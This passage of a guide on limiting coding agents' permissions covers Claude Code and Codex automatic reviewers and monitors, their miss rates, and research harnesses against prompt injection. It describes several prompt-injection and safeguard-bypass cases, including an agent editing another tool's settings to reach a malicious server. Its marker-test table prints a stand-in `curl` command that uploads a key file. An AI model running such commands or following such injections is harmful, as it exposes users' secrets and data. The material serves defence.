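Testers also became less likely to refuse dangerous commands as they saw more prompts, refusing about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The automatic reviewer's refusal rate stayed the same.

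The testers had nothing of their own at stake. The shop owner might look harder at a command that could delete her orders, but she would also understand less of it than a professional tester, so her rate could be higher or lower than 13.6%. The decline over a session is more likely to apply to her, since *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) cites earlier research in which people paid less attention to warnings as they saw more of them. The gap between 89% and 13.6% is too large to dismiss just because Anthropic published the study while promoting its reviewer.

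Anthropic also examined real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the manually approved sessions and 2.4% of those with the automatic reviewer. This evidence is weaker because users chose their own mode and may have used the two modes for different work.

### How Claude Code's auto mode decides

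In Claude Code, the automatic reviewer is called the classifier, and the mode that uses it is called auto mode. The steps below combine Anthropic's March account with the current rules in its *Choose a permission mode*.

1. **Rules.** Claude Code first applies the operator's own rules, which can block an action, force an approval prompt or allow the action. It ignores rules that would allow almost any command, such as one that permits every Python program.
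2. **Reading and edits in the project.** It allows most reading, and edits to files in the project folder, without a review. Some files, such as its own settings, are exceptions.
3. **Fast filter.** Most other actions go to the classifier, which gives a single yes-or-no answer without reasoning. Its instructions tell it to block when in doubt.
4. **Reasoned check.** If the filter flags an action, the classifier examines the same material again, this time reasoning step by step before it decides.
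5. **Fallback.** If the classifier blocks the action, Claude looks for a safer way to do the job. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, auto mode pauses and Claude Code asks the user.

In step 2, Anthropic skips the review of project edits because developers can inspect them later in the project's version history. The shop's owner can't read code, so a leak hidden in `delivery.js` could get past both the classifier and her.

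The classifier receives the user's messages, the standing instructions in `CLAUDE.md` and the actions Claude has taken or proposed. It doesn't receive Claude's explanations, which might persuade it to allow something harmful. It also doesn't receive other files, web pages or command output, because these might contain a prompt injection. A separate check scans such text for injected instructions and warns Claude about them.

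This design makes the classifier harder to trick, but it also means the classifier sees fewer facts. If Claude proposes a refund for order 1184, the classifier can't see the order record that shows whether the parcel was late, so it has to judge from what the owner asked for.

She should therefore name the exact action she wants. Under Anthropic's rules, a direct request authorises Claude to overwrite the project's history on a server, but "clean up the repo" doesn't. Similarly, she could write "refund order 1184 in full" instead of "sort out the late parcels". If she writes "don't publish anything", the classifier treats that as a reason to block publishing. But a rule that denies the action lasts longer than her message, which may disappear when Claude Code shortens a long conversation.

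By default, auto mode lets Claude read a project's `.env` file and send the credentials in it to the service they belong to, so users still need to remove old passwords.

### How often auto mode is wrong

In March, Anthropic ran auto mode on 10,000 real actions by its employees' agents, and auto mode wrongly blocked 0.4% of the harmless ones. Anthropic also tested it on 52 real cases in which an agent had gone further than the user wanted, and it missed 17% of them.

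The reasoned check makes auto mode less annoying but somewhat less safe. The fast filter alone would have blocked 8.5% of harmless actions and missed 6.6% of dangerous ones. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier correctly identified the action as dangerous but wrongly classed it as approved by the user. It might, for example, have counted the user's approval of an earlier, similar action as approval of this one.

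Anthropic has since published lower miss rates, but they come from other tests:

| Test | Cases | Miss rate |
|---|---|---|
| Real cases of agents exceeding a request, March | 52 | 17% |
| Synthetic attempts to send data out, March | 1,000 | 5.7% |
| Commands planted in the tester study, August | 1,053 | 11% |
| Synthetic attacks by Apollo Research, before and after changes | Not stated | 12%, then 7% |

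The percentages in the column fall from 17% to 7%, but they measure different things, so they don't show steady progress. Clearly dangerous commands are probably easier to recognise than an agent's overeager attempt to help, and attackers design synthetic attacks to find weak points. The 17% is also imprecise because it comes from only 52 cases, which gives a standard 95% confidence interval of about 9% to 30%.

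Auto mode got better at catching attacks after tests by Apollo Research, a British AI safety company. Apollo inserted attacks into records of real coding sessions and gave Anthropic some of the successful ones. Anthropic then gave the classifier more information about the project, such as whether its repository was public. On a second set of attacks that Anthropic had never seen, auto mode caught about half of those it had previously missed and missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. Nobody has published a repeat of the test on real overeager actions, the cases most like the accidents at PocketOS and DataTalks.Club.

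### Auto mode becomes the default

In March, Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* introduced the feature as a research preview for one business plan and still recommended using it in isolated environments. From 14 August, new sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans started in auto mode unless the user had chosen another default. On 22 October, Anthropic announced that most Claude apps on these plans would follow the next week.

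The change has since reached other customers. According to Anthropic, interactive sessions in a terminal or the VS Code editor normally start in auto mode from version 2.1.283 of Claude Code. The *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), checked against the program on 12 November, lists auto mode as the starting mode on every plan. Scripted runs still start in Manual mode, where Claude Code asks the user for approval.

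An operator who wants Manual mode, for example because she relies on the sandbox, now has to select it. She can press Shift+Tab in the terminal until the status bar shows "manual mode on". To keep Manual mode for all terminal sessions, she can set `permissions.defaultMode` in her personal settings file to `default`, which still means Manual despite its name. She can't switch modes by asking Claude in the chat.

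Manual mode is useful to a non-expert only if she is willing to refuse actions she doesn't understand. If she would approve everything anyway, auto mode is safer. For high-stakes changes to live systems, Anthropic still recommends that users review Claude's actions themselves.

### Codex's automatic review

Codex sends approval prompts to the user by default, but an operator can send them to an automatic reviewer by setting `approvals_reviewer` to `auto_review`. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, this reviewer reviews only actions that would otherwise need approval, such as contacting a blocked address or writing outside the permitted folders. Actions that the sandbox already allows run without review, so Codex has the same gap as auto mode, in that edits to `delivery.js` are not reviewed.

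*Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) gives an illustration from OpenAI's internal use in which 9,280 of 10,000 actions stayed inside the sandbox and needed no review. Manual approval would have interrupted the user for each of the other 720. The automatic reviewer approved 713 of them and denied 7. After four of the denials, Codex found a safer way to continue, and after the other three it stopped and asked the user.

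This reviewer approves about 99% of requests, a higher share than Claude Code's human users do, so the approval rate alone is a poor measure of review quality. Tests with known dangerous actions are more informative. On OpenAI's own synthetic test sets, the reviewer denied 90.3% of actions that went beyond the user's request and 99.3% of prompt-injection attempts to run hostile code, steal secrets or upload files. When the prompt-injection tests also included destructive deletions and data tampering, it denied 90.2%. Trębacz and colleagues explain that the reviewer allowed most of the additional cases because they weren't serious enough, though they might be serious for a small shop without good backups.

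Unlike Claude Code's classifier, the Codex reviewer normally receives tool output as well as the user's messages. It could therefore read in the order record that a parcel arrived late, but it would also read any misleading instruction a customer had typed there. OpenAI's testers found ways to mislead it into approving commands.

Codex stops the agent's current turn after three denials in a row, or ten in the last 50 reviews. If a review fails or times out, the action doesn't run. The user can approve a denied action for one retry, but the reviewer checks it again and may still refuse. OpenAI warns that the feature "is not a deterministic security guarantee".

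The owner's profile for the delivery fee sets approvals to `never`, so Codex has no requests to review. Claude Code's nearest equivalent is `dontAsk` mode, which denies any action that would normally prompt for approval.

### Tests with prompt injection

Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs, an outside testing company, to compare the two products as they stood on 17 July 2026. Trajectory Labs prepared 72 scenarios containing outside text meant to make the agent do something harmful and irreversible, such as leaking private data, and ran each one ten times.

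| Product and model | Mode | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 | Auto mode | 0 of 720 |
| Claude Code with Anthropic's latest models | No permission checks | 0.09% on average |
| Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol | Auto-review | 5.83% |
| Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol | Full Access | 19.03% |

The Claude models resisted nearly every attack even without auto mode, so most of the difference between the products comes from the models, not the reviewers. In Codex, attacks succeeded much less often with Auto-review than with Full Access. But Full Access also removes the sandbox, so the reviewer may account for only part of that difference.

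Trajectory Labs used its own browser connection instead of the companies' own, which have additional protections. OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published the results. The 720 attempts covered only 72 different scenarios.

Willison (2026) describes another researcher's tests, in which malicious code ran despite auto mode. In a few runs, auto mode then stopped Claude from shutting the code down. Willison and the researcher both conclude that unattended agents should run in a sandbox, container or virtual machine.

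### Expected loss and worst loss

A simple formula shows what a reviewer can improve:

expected loss = dangerous attempts × miss rate × average harm

Suppose the shop's agent makes ten dangerous attempts a year. If it holds the token for the whole hosting account, the average harm is $2,000 and the worst is $60,000, for losing the website, orders and backups together. If it can reach only the test environment, the average is $50 and the worst is $300. The dollar amounts and the number of attempts are invented, but the miss rates, 86.4% for people and 11% for the automatic reviewer, come from the tester study.

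| What the agent can reach | Who reviews its actions | Calculation | Expected loss per year | Worst single loss |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Whole hosting account | The owner, as attentive as the testers | 10 × 0.864 × $2,000 | $17,280 | $60,000 |
| Whole hosting account | Automatic reviewer | 10 × 0.11 × $2,000 | $2,200 | $60,000 |
| Test environment | Nobody | 10 × 1 × $50 | $500 | $300 |
| Test environment | Automatic reviewer | 10 × 0.11 × $50 | $55 | $300 |

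The automatic reviewer cuts the expected loss by 87%, but one miss can still cost $60,000. Only the narrower grant reduces the cost of a miss. With these numbers, an unreviewed agent confined to the test environment also has a lower expected loss than a reviewed agent with access to the whole account.

People may give an agent more work once it interrupts them less, and it would then make more dangerous attempts. In this example, the number of attempts would have to rise nearly eightfold to cancel out the reviewer's advantage over the owner. An agent may also try again after a block. If the reviewer has an independent 11% chance of missing each attempt, at least one of three attempts at the same harmful result gets through about 30% of the time. Both products therefore stop after a few blocks in a row.

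### What the operator should still decide

The owner should make the decision herself when an action affects something outside the agent's working copy and she couldn't undo it. At the shop, that leaves five kinds of action:

- publishing to the live website
- moving money
- sending a message to a customer or anyone else outside the business
- deleting live data or a backup
- giving the agent more access

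If the user can't say in one sentence what an action will change, she should refuse it. She can leave everything not on her short list to the sandbox and the automatic reviewer. The list needs to be short because her attention is limited. In simulations that assumed each prompt makes the next approval more likely, *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026) found that fewer prompts helped only if the remaining ones were about the actions that mattered.

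She should also approve the plan before the agent starts. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) lists this as one way to avoid asking about every step. Claude Code's plan mode normally blocks edits until the user accepts the plan. She has to read the options for accepting it, because one also switches the session to auto mode. The agent may not follow the accepted plan, so the five kinds of action still need their own decision.

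In Claude Code, a user can write an `ask` rule that forces an approval prompt for a chosen action, even in auto mode. Like other rules that match a command's text, it can miss the same command written another way, as Anthropic points out for `git push`, which uploads code. An approval step in the service itself, such as Stripe's page for approving a refund, is more reliable because it applies however the agent words its request. Stripe's page is also easier for a non-expert to understand than a command.

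An approval threshold on individual payments can fail. In one scenario from *Approve What, Exactly?*, an agent avoided approval by splitting a payment into small pieces, and only a limit on the total prevented this. If the owner tells Stripe to hold refunds above $50 for approval, an agent could still make a hundred refunds of $40. If she tells it to hold every refund, refunding thirty late parcels takes thirty approvals, and she may start approving them without checking.

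She can ask the agent for one list of the late parcels, with each order number, promised date, arrival date and refund amount. She then checks the dates against the courier's records, adds up the total and issues the refunds herself. This way, the agent needs a copy of the delivery records but no key that can move money.

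## Passing authority to sub-agents and taking it back

A coding agent can start sub-agents to do parts of a task. If the shop owner asks an agent to correct the delivery fee and test the result, it might start one sub-agent to edit `delivery.js` and another to run the tests. If a single grant covers the whole task, the sub-agent that runs the tests can also edit the file. The grant also lasts until the task ends, so an agent that needs the courier's spreadsheet for two minutes can still open it an hour later.

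According to Anthropic's *Create custom subagents*, a Claude Code sub-agent inherits nearly all the main conversation's tools, including those of connected services, unless the user lists fewer. Codex sub-agents inherit the current sandbox policy by default, according to OpenAI's *Subagents*. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* argues that a sub-agent that only needs to write a summary shouldn't inherit permission to change anything.

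Some research prototypes divide a grant more finely. CapScope, the harness from Bouras and colleagues, gives each agent its own permissions. PORTICO withdraws a permission when the step that needed it ends.

### CapScope

CapScope decides the most a task may do before any agent has read a file that an attacker could have written.

1. A separate model call reads the user's request and the names of the project's files, but not their contents. It predicts which files and commands the task will need.
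2. Ordinary code checks the prediction and turns it into a ceiling for the whole task. Nothing that an agent reads later can raise the ceiling.
3. The main agent gets permissions of its own, which may only allow reading.
4. When the main agent starts a sub-agent, it requests permissions for it. The harness adds any that the sub-agent's role obviously requires, then discards everything outside the ceiling.
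5. Before each tool call, the harness looks up the permissions of the agent that proposed it. If none of them covers the call, the harness refuses it.

The harness stores the permissions outside the model's context, so an injected instruction can change what an agent requests but can't edit the permissions. File names could also carry injected instructions, since anyone who can add a file to a project chooses its name. Bouras and colleagues did not test this.

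Each permission combines a kind of action (read, write or run) with a scope, such as a folder or a command. If D is the ceiling and R is the set of permissions requested for a sub-agent, the sub-agent receives

S = { r ∈ R : r ⪯ c for some c ∈ D }.

Here r ⪯ c means that r and c allow the same kind of action, and that c covers every file or command that r covers. A sub-agent gets each requested permission that fits entirely inside a permission in the ceiling. CapScope drops a request that is too wide instead of narrowing it. If a sub-agent starts other agents, its permissions become their ceiling.

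In the example with the planted security key, the ceiling allows reading anything in the project, writing in the source folder `src`, and running the two checking programs `pytest` and `mypy`. The main agent starts a test runner and requests permission for it to read the `tests` folder and run `pytest`. Both permissions are within the ceiling, so the runner gets them. It runs the tests, reads the note with instructions to replace the key, and proposes to write to `src/auth/keys.py`. The harness blocks the write because the runner has no permission to write. A second sub-agent, the patcher, can still edit the source code to make the repair.

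The subset rule alone would not have stopped this attack. The ceiling allows writing in `src`, so the runner would have received that permission if the main agent had requested it. The protection also depends on the main agent requesting few permissions.

*The Agent Operating System (AOS)* (2026) extends the rule to time and budgets. A sub-agent's permission may not outlast its parent's, and the budgets of sub-agents working at the same time may not add up to more than the parent has left. Without this budget limit, a main agent with $100 to spend on refunds could start two sub-agents with $100 each.

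### The test of CapScope

Bouras and colleagues ran 300 repairs on five small Python projects, each with one bug. They planted a harmful instruction in one of five places, such as a README file or the test output, and compared CapScope with three other arrangements. Each of the four arrangements had 75 runs with the same main agent, test runner, patcher and verifier, all using the model qwen3.5-flash.

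| Permissions | Planted action carried out | Repairs completed | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| No limits | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 s |
| A fixed list of forbidden paths and commands | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 s |
| One policy written for the task and shared by all agents | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 s |
| CapScope | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 s |

The fixed list made almost no difference because the planted actions looked like ordinary project work, such as writing to a project file. The shared policy helped more, but it had to include every permission any agent needed. CapScope, which divides the permissions between agents, took longer than the shared policy in this test but completed as many repairs.

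The model was still easy to mislead. Under CapScope, an agent proposed the planted action in 34 runs, and the harness blocked it in all but three. The three successful attacks all came through `AGENTS.md`, an instruction file that the harness loads automatically. Bouras and colleagues attribute CapScope's remaining weakness to permissions wider than the subtask needs and to injected text that influences what the main agent requests for a sub-agent.

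Seven repairs failed under CapScope. In two, the prediction had left out permission to write the source code. In another two, the test runner found the right correction but the agents never passed it to the patcher. The last three ran out of time although the tests were passing.

Some of the delay came from agents repeating proposals that the harness had refused. A person watching could stop the agent after the first refusal, but an unattended agent keeps repeating the proposal, and the operator pays for the extra model use.

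### PORTICO

Under CapScope, a permission lasts as long as the agent that holds it. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) examines agents that keep working after they no longer need a permission. Its prototype, PORTICO, follows a contract written before the task. The contract lists what the agent may use from the start, what it may request later, what is always forbidden, and which events end a temporary permission.

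In his main example, an agent has to add an optional timeout to a program. The change starts in `src/api.py` but also affects `src/serialization.py`.

1. At the start, the agent can read and edit `src/api.py` and its test file, and run that test.
2. It tries to read some notes about packaging. PORTICO refuses because the contract forbids them.
3. It requests access to `src/serialization.py`, which the contract allows on request.
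4. PORTICO grants the request by issuing handles, which are capabilities valid only for this grant. The agent has not opened the file yet.
5. The agent uses the handles to read and edit the file.
6. The tests pass, and PORTICO closes the grant. It removes the handles from the list of tools the agent sees.
7. The agent tries an old handle again, and PORTICO refuses it.

Closing a grant stops the model from acting on the file, but the file's name and whatever the model read there stay in its context. Closing a grant therefore protects against later changes better than against leaks.

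PORTICO keeps a grant open or ends it based only on events from outside the model, such as the result of a test that PORTICO itself started, a change of workflow phase, or a decision by a person. An agent's statement that it has finished doesn't affect the grant.

To isolate the effect of closure, Santos-Grueiro built a comparator that started with the same permissions and received the same grants at the same moments, but never withdrew them. PORTICO and the comparator both completed the task in all 10 runs. When the agent tried to read the file again after the step had ended, PORTICO rejected all 10 attempts and the comparator permitted them all. In six other cases, a model received an injected instruction to reuse an old handle to write a file, alter Git's records or contact a network address. The comparator carried out all six actions, while PORTICO carried out none of them.

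The comparator had no way to refuse, so these scores confirm that PORTICO's revocation works as designed. They don't measure how often a real agent would misuse a leftover permission, and Santos-Grueiro doesn't present them as a rate.

Restricting an agent's permissions can leave work unfinished. On 37 coding tasks, each run five times, an agent with only its starting permissions succeeded in 21% of runs. Allowing it to request more raised that to 87%, while an ordinary fixed list of allowed tools and files reached 97%. On real open-source projects, PORTICO completed 31 of 42 runs, and a version without revocation completed all 42. Some contracts closed a grant too early or gave the agent no way to reopen it, and sometimes the model didn't request a new one. An operator would see a job that stopped halfway, which is annoying but easier to notice than a permission someone forgot to revoke.

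Revocation can also arrive late. If a command is already running when its grant is revoked, the harness has to check the handle again just before the command takes effect. *The Agent Operating System (AOS)* recommends short expiry times for risky permissions, because a cancellation may not immediately reach a disconnected task.

### AgentCap and CaMeL

CapScope and PORTICO check which files or tools an agent is allowed to use, but an agent allowed to send a payment can still send it to the wrong person. AgentCap and CaMeL also check where the details of an action came from.

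*AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) requires a new short-lived token for every tool call. In its banking example, a token for sending money lasts 30 seconds and works once. The agent must already hold a valid token for checking the balance, and the recipient must appear in a trusted source, such as the user's request. If the recipient appears only in a document the agent has read, the system refuses the payment.

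In AgentCap, an agent can pass a token to a sub-agent with the same or a shorter lifetime and the same number of uses or fewer. The action and the resource stay the same, so an agent can't narrow a token from a folder to one file, as it could in CapScope. AgentCap also withdraws permissions based on an agent's behaviour. Each agent starts with a trust score of 0.8, and each refused or abnormal call multiplies the score by 0.7. After two such calls in a row the agent loses permission to write, and after three it loses all permissions, even if it is honest and has only guessed wrongly.

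CaMeL (Debenedetti and colleagues, 2025) protects the plan. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) describes how it divides the work between two models. The first sees the user's request and descriptions of the tools, and writes a short program that sets out every step. The second reads emails, web pages and other untrusted text, but has no tools. A hidden instruction in that text can change the second model's summary and influence which of the planned branches the program takes, but it can't add a step. CaMeL also tracks where each value came from, so a policy can, for example, stop private data from going to someone who isn't allowed to see it.

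On AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, banking and travel tasks, AgentCap reduced the success rate of attacks from 45.6% to 5.1% on GPT-4o and from 33.2% to zero on GPT-5.4. When there was no attack, AgentCap lowered the share of tasks completed by 3.1 percentage points for GPT-4o and 7.2 for GPT-5.4. Each check took less than 0.2 milliseconds. Some of the remaining attacks succeeded because the policy had not marked an argument as sensitive or a source as untrusted. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao wrote each policy from the benchmark's own task descriptions, so policies will probably fit less well when an operator's requests vary from day to day.

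CaMeL has bigger drawbacks. When Peters-Gill and colleagues tested it on 112 professional tasks that a main agent divided among sub-agents, task success fell by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that with GPT-4o, CaMeL made the model read about 2.8 times as much text and write about 2.7 times as much on a typical task. *CapLite* (2026) reports that on small models, CaMeL let through only 20 of 13,935 attacks but processed more than three times as much text per task as an undefended agent.

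CaMeL is also not well suited to repairing code. Its planning model has to write the program that calls the tools before seeing what they return, but someone looking for a bug usually chooses which file to open next based on what the last one contained. Bouras and colleagues point out that its evaluation covered web and email agents, not coding.

CaMeL's guarantee applies to one agent and can fail when that agent passes text to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues asked a group of CaMeL agents to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague. The database contained a hidden instruction to email the data to an outside address. The main agent never acted on the instruction, but copied the summary into its request to the sub-agent that sends messages. That sub-agent treated the whole request, including the hidden instruction, as coming from its user, and emailed the data to the outside address.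 *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (Ji, Wu and colleagues, 2026) classes such messages as confused-deputy attacks.

Peters-Gill and colleagues repaired this by sending instructions and data to the sub-agent separately, so that the sub-agent's planning model never reads the data. In their multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent used CaMeL alone, and never with the repair. The 12.9% is an average over models that differed widely. Even without CaMeL, attacks succeeded only 1.5% of the time against Fable 5 and never against GPT-5.5. Stronger attacks might well have succeeded, but on this evidence a user of the newest models would take on most of CaMeL's drawbacks for a small measured benefit.

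### Limits the prototypes share

The evidence comes mostly from small or artificial tests. CapScope has been tested on five small projects with one model. Santos-Grueiro built most of PORTICO's tasks for the experiment. He checked for reuse of old handles using separate files that PORTICO never reads, but counted other forbidden actions using the same contracts that PORTICO enforces. If a contract wrongly allowed an action, that count could miss it. AgentCap's main results come from a single run of each test.

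Someone also has to write the rules. PORTICO and AgentCap rely on contracts and policies written by people who understand the tools, and Santos-Grueiro did not measure how long writing them takes. Even experts make mistakes. AgentCap's checking program found two contradictory rules in a customer-service policy that made it impossible for any agent to delete a customer. CapScope has a model predict the permissions instead, but AuthBench showed that models often leave out permissions a task needs and include ones it doesn't.

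A permitted command can also run other code, as `pytest` does when it runs the shop's tests. In the example with the planted key, the attacker's test file could write the new key directly into the source code when `pytest` runs it. CapScope could not refuse that write, because no agent would have proposed a tool call for it. PORTICO has the same limitation, so both need a process sandbox underneath.

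None of the four systems can check whether an agent has used a permission well. AgentCap, for example, could check who receives a payment but not whether a line of code is correct.

### Separate sessions for separate steps

The shop owner can get some of the same protection by dividing a job into sessions and giving each its own grant. Suppose twenty customers have written to complain about delivery fees, and she wants an agent to find out what went wrong. Strangers wrote the messages, so the messages may contain instructions meant for the agent.

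| Session | What the agent may do | When she closes it |
|---|---|---|
| Read the complaints | Read a copy of the messages, and nothing else | When she has a list of order numbers and fees |
| Find the fault | Read the copy of the website's code | When the agent has named the file |
| Correct it | Read the code, change that file, run the tests | When her test orders show the right fees |

Closing a session serves the same purpose as PORTICO's closure event, and she decides when to do it. A new session also starts without the text of the last one, so an instruction hidden in a complaint doesn't carry over unless the agent saved it in a file or in its memory. However, she has to explain the problem again each time.

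She shouldn't paste the first session's summary into the next request. Pasted text reaches the agent as if it were her own instruction, which is how the hidden message got through in the experiment with the job applicants. She can instead check the order numbers against her records and type them in herself.

In Codex, she can make the first two sessions read-only by using a permission profile without the line that allows writing, and by starting the agent in a folder that holds only the messages or only the code. According to OpenAI, Codex also has a general read-only mode in which the agent needs approval to edit files or run commands. But that mode doesn't limit reading to one folder.

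Starting a new session doesn't clear every old permission. According to Anthropic, when a Claude Code user answers an approval prompt with "Yes, don't ask again", permission to edit files ends with the session, but permission to run a shell command is permanent for that project. Claude Code stores the permanent permission in `.claude/settings.local.json`. Before a new task, the user can type `/permissions` to see the saved rules and remove any that the task doesn't need.

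Sub-agents inside one session offer weaker separation, though they are still better than giving every agent everything. In Claude Code, she could define one that only reads:

```yaml
---
name: complaint-reader
description: Lists the order numbers and fees in customer messages
tools: Read
---
```

The `tools` line is easy to get wrong. If she leaves it out or types `tool` instead, Claude Code reports no error and the sub-agent inherits the usual tools. If she adds `Bash`, the sub-agent can change files through shell commands. She also can't rely on the separate `permissionMode` setting, because Claude Code ignores it when the main conversation is in auto mode, now the usual default. The sub-agent's report still goes to a main agent with wider powers, although auto mode reviews it first.

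Codex starts sub-agents only when the user asks for them. OpenAI describes how to make a sub-agent read-only by setting `sandbox_mode` in its settings file, but this older setting can make Codex ignore a permission profile, so the sub-agent may be able to read much more of her laptop than the profile allows. Permissions she has changed during the session also override the sub-agent's file. For this job, she is better off using separate sessions instead of sub-agents. In Claude Code, she can block sub-agents with a rule that denies the `Agent` tool, since deny rules apply in every mode.

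If she has to stop a job in a hurry, she should check that any sub-agents have stopped too. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) warns that sub-agents can keep running after someone shuts down the agent that started them. Claude Code lists running sub-agents under `/tasks`, and Codex lets her switch between them with `/agent`. If she isn't sure she has found them all, she can cancel the job's tokens at the hosting and payment companies, which cuts off every agent using those tokens.

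## Testing the limits and preparing to recover

The shop owner now has a written grant, a permission profile and a set of narrow tokens. A mistyped folder name or a forgotten setting could still leave her tax records open to the agent, and she might never see an error. She can test the limits by asking the agent to try a few forbidden actions on items she wouldn't mind losing. She also needs a way to recover, because the agent may damage something it has permission to change.

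### The marker tests

She prepares three kinds of marker:

- a file called `marker.txt` in her business folder, containing an invented phrase
- a file called `fake-key.txt` in the copy of the website, containing an invented password
- a fake customer in the live database, `marker-live@example.com`, and another in the test database, `marker-test@example.com`

She then starts the agent as she would for real work, tells it she is testing its permissions with invented data, and asks it to run each command exactly as written and show the full output. The first three tests suit the delivery-fee job, and the last suits the checkout job, where the agent has a login to the test database. The commands are for a Mac.

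| Ask the agent to | Expected result | What a pass doesn't prove |
|---|---|---|
| Read the marker: `cat ~/Business/marker.txt` | An error, and no sign of the phrase | That other folders are closed, or that a connected service can't open the file |
| Delete the marker: `rm ~/Business/marker.txt` | An error, and the file is still there when she looks | That files inside the grant are safe |
| Send the fake password: `curl -d @fake-key.txt https://example.com` | The connection fails | That the agent can't send data through an address it is allowed to contact |
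| Delete `marker-live@example.com`, using its database login | No such customer, and the record is still in the live database | That no other credential reaches the live database |

Each test of a forbidden action needs a matching test of a permitted one, because a command can also fail for an unrelated reason, such as a spelling mistake. The agent should be able to read a file in the website copy, create and delete a file in the temporary folder, and delete `marker-test@example.com`. The delivery-fee profile allows no connections, so the owner runs the `curl` command in her own terminal instead. If the site replies, it was working when the agent failed to reach it.

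*Distributing Security Controls Through Harness Engineering* (Gore, 2026) used similar pairs in 23 simple tests for coding agents. An agent had to reach one website and fail to reach another, then create, read and change a file in one folder and fail to do so in another. The tests showed that some limits worked in one product but not in another. When Gore tried to block file deletion through the permission settings of Claude Code and Codex, Claude Code's score on the relevant tests rose from 50% to 100%, while Codex's stayed at 50%.

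The owner should count a test as passed only if the agent ran the command and the operating system or the service refused it. If the agent declines to run the command, she has tested only the model's caution, which may differ next time. In one of Gore's tests, an agent with no protection against hidden instructions avoided a malicious document after it happened to notice a security scanner among its tools and became more careful. It never did so again in similar tests.

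Four markers also can't cover everything an agent might try. Gore asked an agent called Pi to connect to a malicious MCP server. Pi can't do that, so it searched the disk, found a copy of Claude Code and added the server to Claude Code's settings. For a broader check, an operator can have the agent run ControlPlane's *sandbox-probe*, a free program that reports what the agent can reach on the computer. The report is more technical than the marker tests, and ControlPlane notes that the program doesn't prevent an agent from rewriting the output.

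### Running the tests in the agent's session

The owner's terminal runs outside the agent's sandbox, so the forbidden commands would succeed there even if the sandbox worked perfectly. Anthropic warns that commands typed at Claude Code's `!` prompt usually run outside the sandbox too, and tells users to ask Claude to run the test instead. If Claude then offers to retry a failed command without the sandbox, the owner should decline.

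The results of a test also depend on the folder and credentials it uses. Claude Code and Codex load some settings from the project folder, so a test in an empty folder may run under different limits from the real project. Testing the database with the owner's login would only show what she can do.

In Claude Code, she should also ask the agent to open `marker.txt` with its built-in file tool, which follows different rules from shell commands.

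A pass applies only to the set-up she tested, so she should repeat the tests after:

- **An update.** Before version 2.1.285 of Claude Code, a project's settings could turn unsandboxed retries back on after the user had turned them off.
- **A new connector.** A local MCP server runs outside Claude Code's sandbox, so she should ask the agent to try reading the marker through it.
- **A saved approval.** If she answers a request for a new web address with "Yes, and don't ask again", Claude Code keeps that address open in future sessions.

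### When the sandbox doesn't start

By default, Claude Code runs commands without a sandbox if it can't start one. This happens on native Windows, and on Linux when a required program is missing. On recent versions of Ubuntu, the default security policy can also stop the sandbox program from isolating commands, even when it is installed. In May 2026, Anthropic's *Sandboxing* described a warning that appears before commands run unsandboxed, but a user can easily miss it, especially if she has left the agent to work alone.

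She can turn this failure into an error by putting these lines in `~/.claude/settings.json`, her personal settings file:

```json
{
  "sandbox": {
    "enabled": true,
    "failIfUnavailable": true,
    "allowUnsandboxedCommands": false
  }
}
```

The first setting turns the sandbox on. The second makes Claude Code exit at startup if the sandbox is unavailable, as it always is on native Windows. The third turns on strict sandbox mode. She still has to run the marker tests, because a sandbox can start correctly with the wrong folders in its settings. In Codex, the tests would also reveal an old `sandbox_mode` entry overriding her profile, because the agent would be able to read `marker.txt`.

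Claude Code can also hide a password from sandboxed commands by showing them a placeholder, but this too can fail without warning. On Linux, if the operator's search pattern doesn't match the password in its file, Claude Code by default lets commands read the real file. Blocking the whole file is safer for an operator who can't check the pattern.

### Copies the agent can't destroy

Backups limit the damage from an accident, though they don't make one less likely. Among the reports in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* where the researchers could tell whether the user recovered, 31% involved damage that was easy to repair and 29% involved damage that took substantial work to repair. In the other 40%, some or all of the loss was permanent.

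**Version control** lets the owner restore a file the agent has ruined. Git normally keeps the project's history inside the project folder, where an agent with write access can delete it. Git also doesn't save files outside the project or files on the project's ignore list, which often includes password files and large files. A copy of the history on GitHub survives damage to the laptop if the agent has no token that can change that copy.

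**File snapshots** are quicker to use, but Anthropic says Claude Code's don't cover files changed by shell commands, and rewinding usually doesn't restore a sub-agent's edits. Claude Code also deletes a session's snapshots about 30 days after saving the last one. The backup programs built into macOS and Windows cover more files, but the owner should unplug the backup drive before starting an agent.

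**Separate backups** protect the database. Jarmak advises keeping the means of recovery beyond the reach of a single failure. The shop should keep its backups with a second storage company, under a login the owner has never saved on the laptop. The backup service should connect to the database with a read-only login and collect the data itself. If a script on the laptop uploaded the backups, the agent might find the script's password and delete them. The backup account should also require a code from her phone at login, so access to her email isn't enough to open it.

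The owner needs old backups as well as recent ones. In reports where the researchers knew whether and when the user noticed the harm, the user noticed at once in 83%, later in 10% and never in 8%. If an agent corrupts customers' addresses on Monday and she notices on Friday, a service that keeps only the last 24 hourly backups will have no copy of the correct addresses. She could keep hourly backups for two days and daily ones for a month. Every few months, she should restore a recent backup into an empty database and check that yesterday's orders are there.

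### File systems with an undo step

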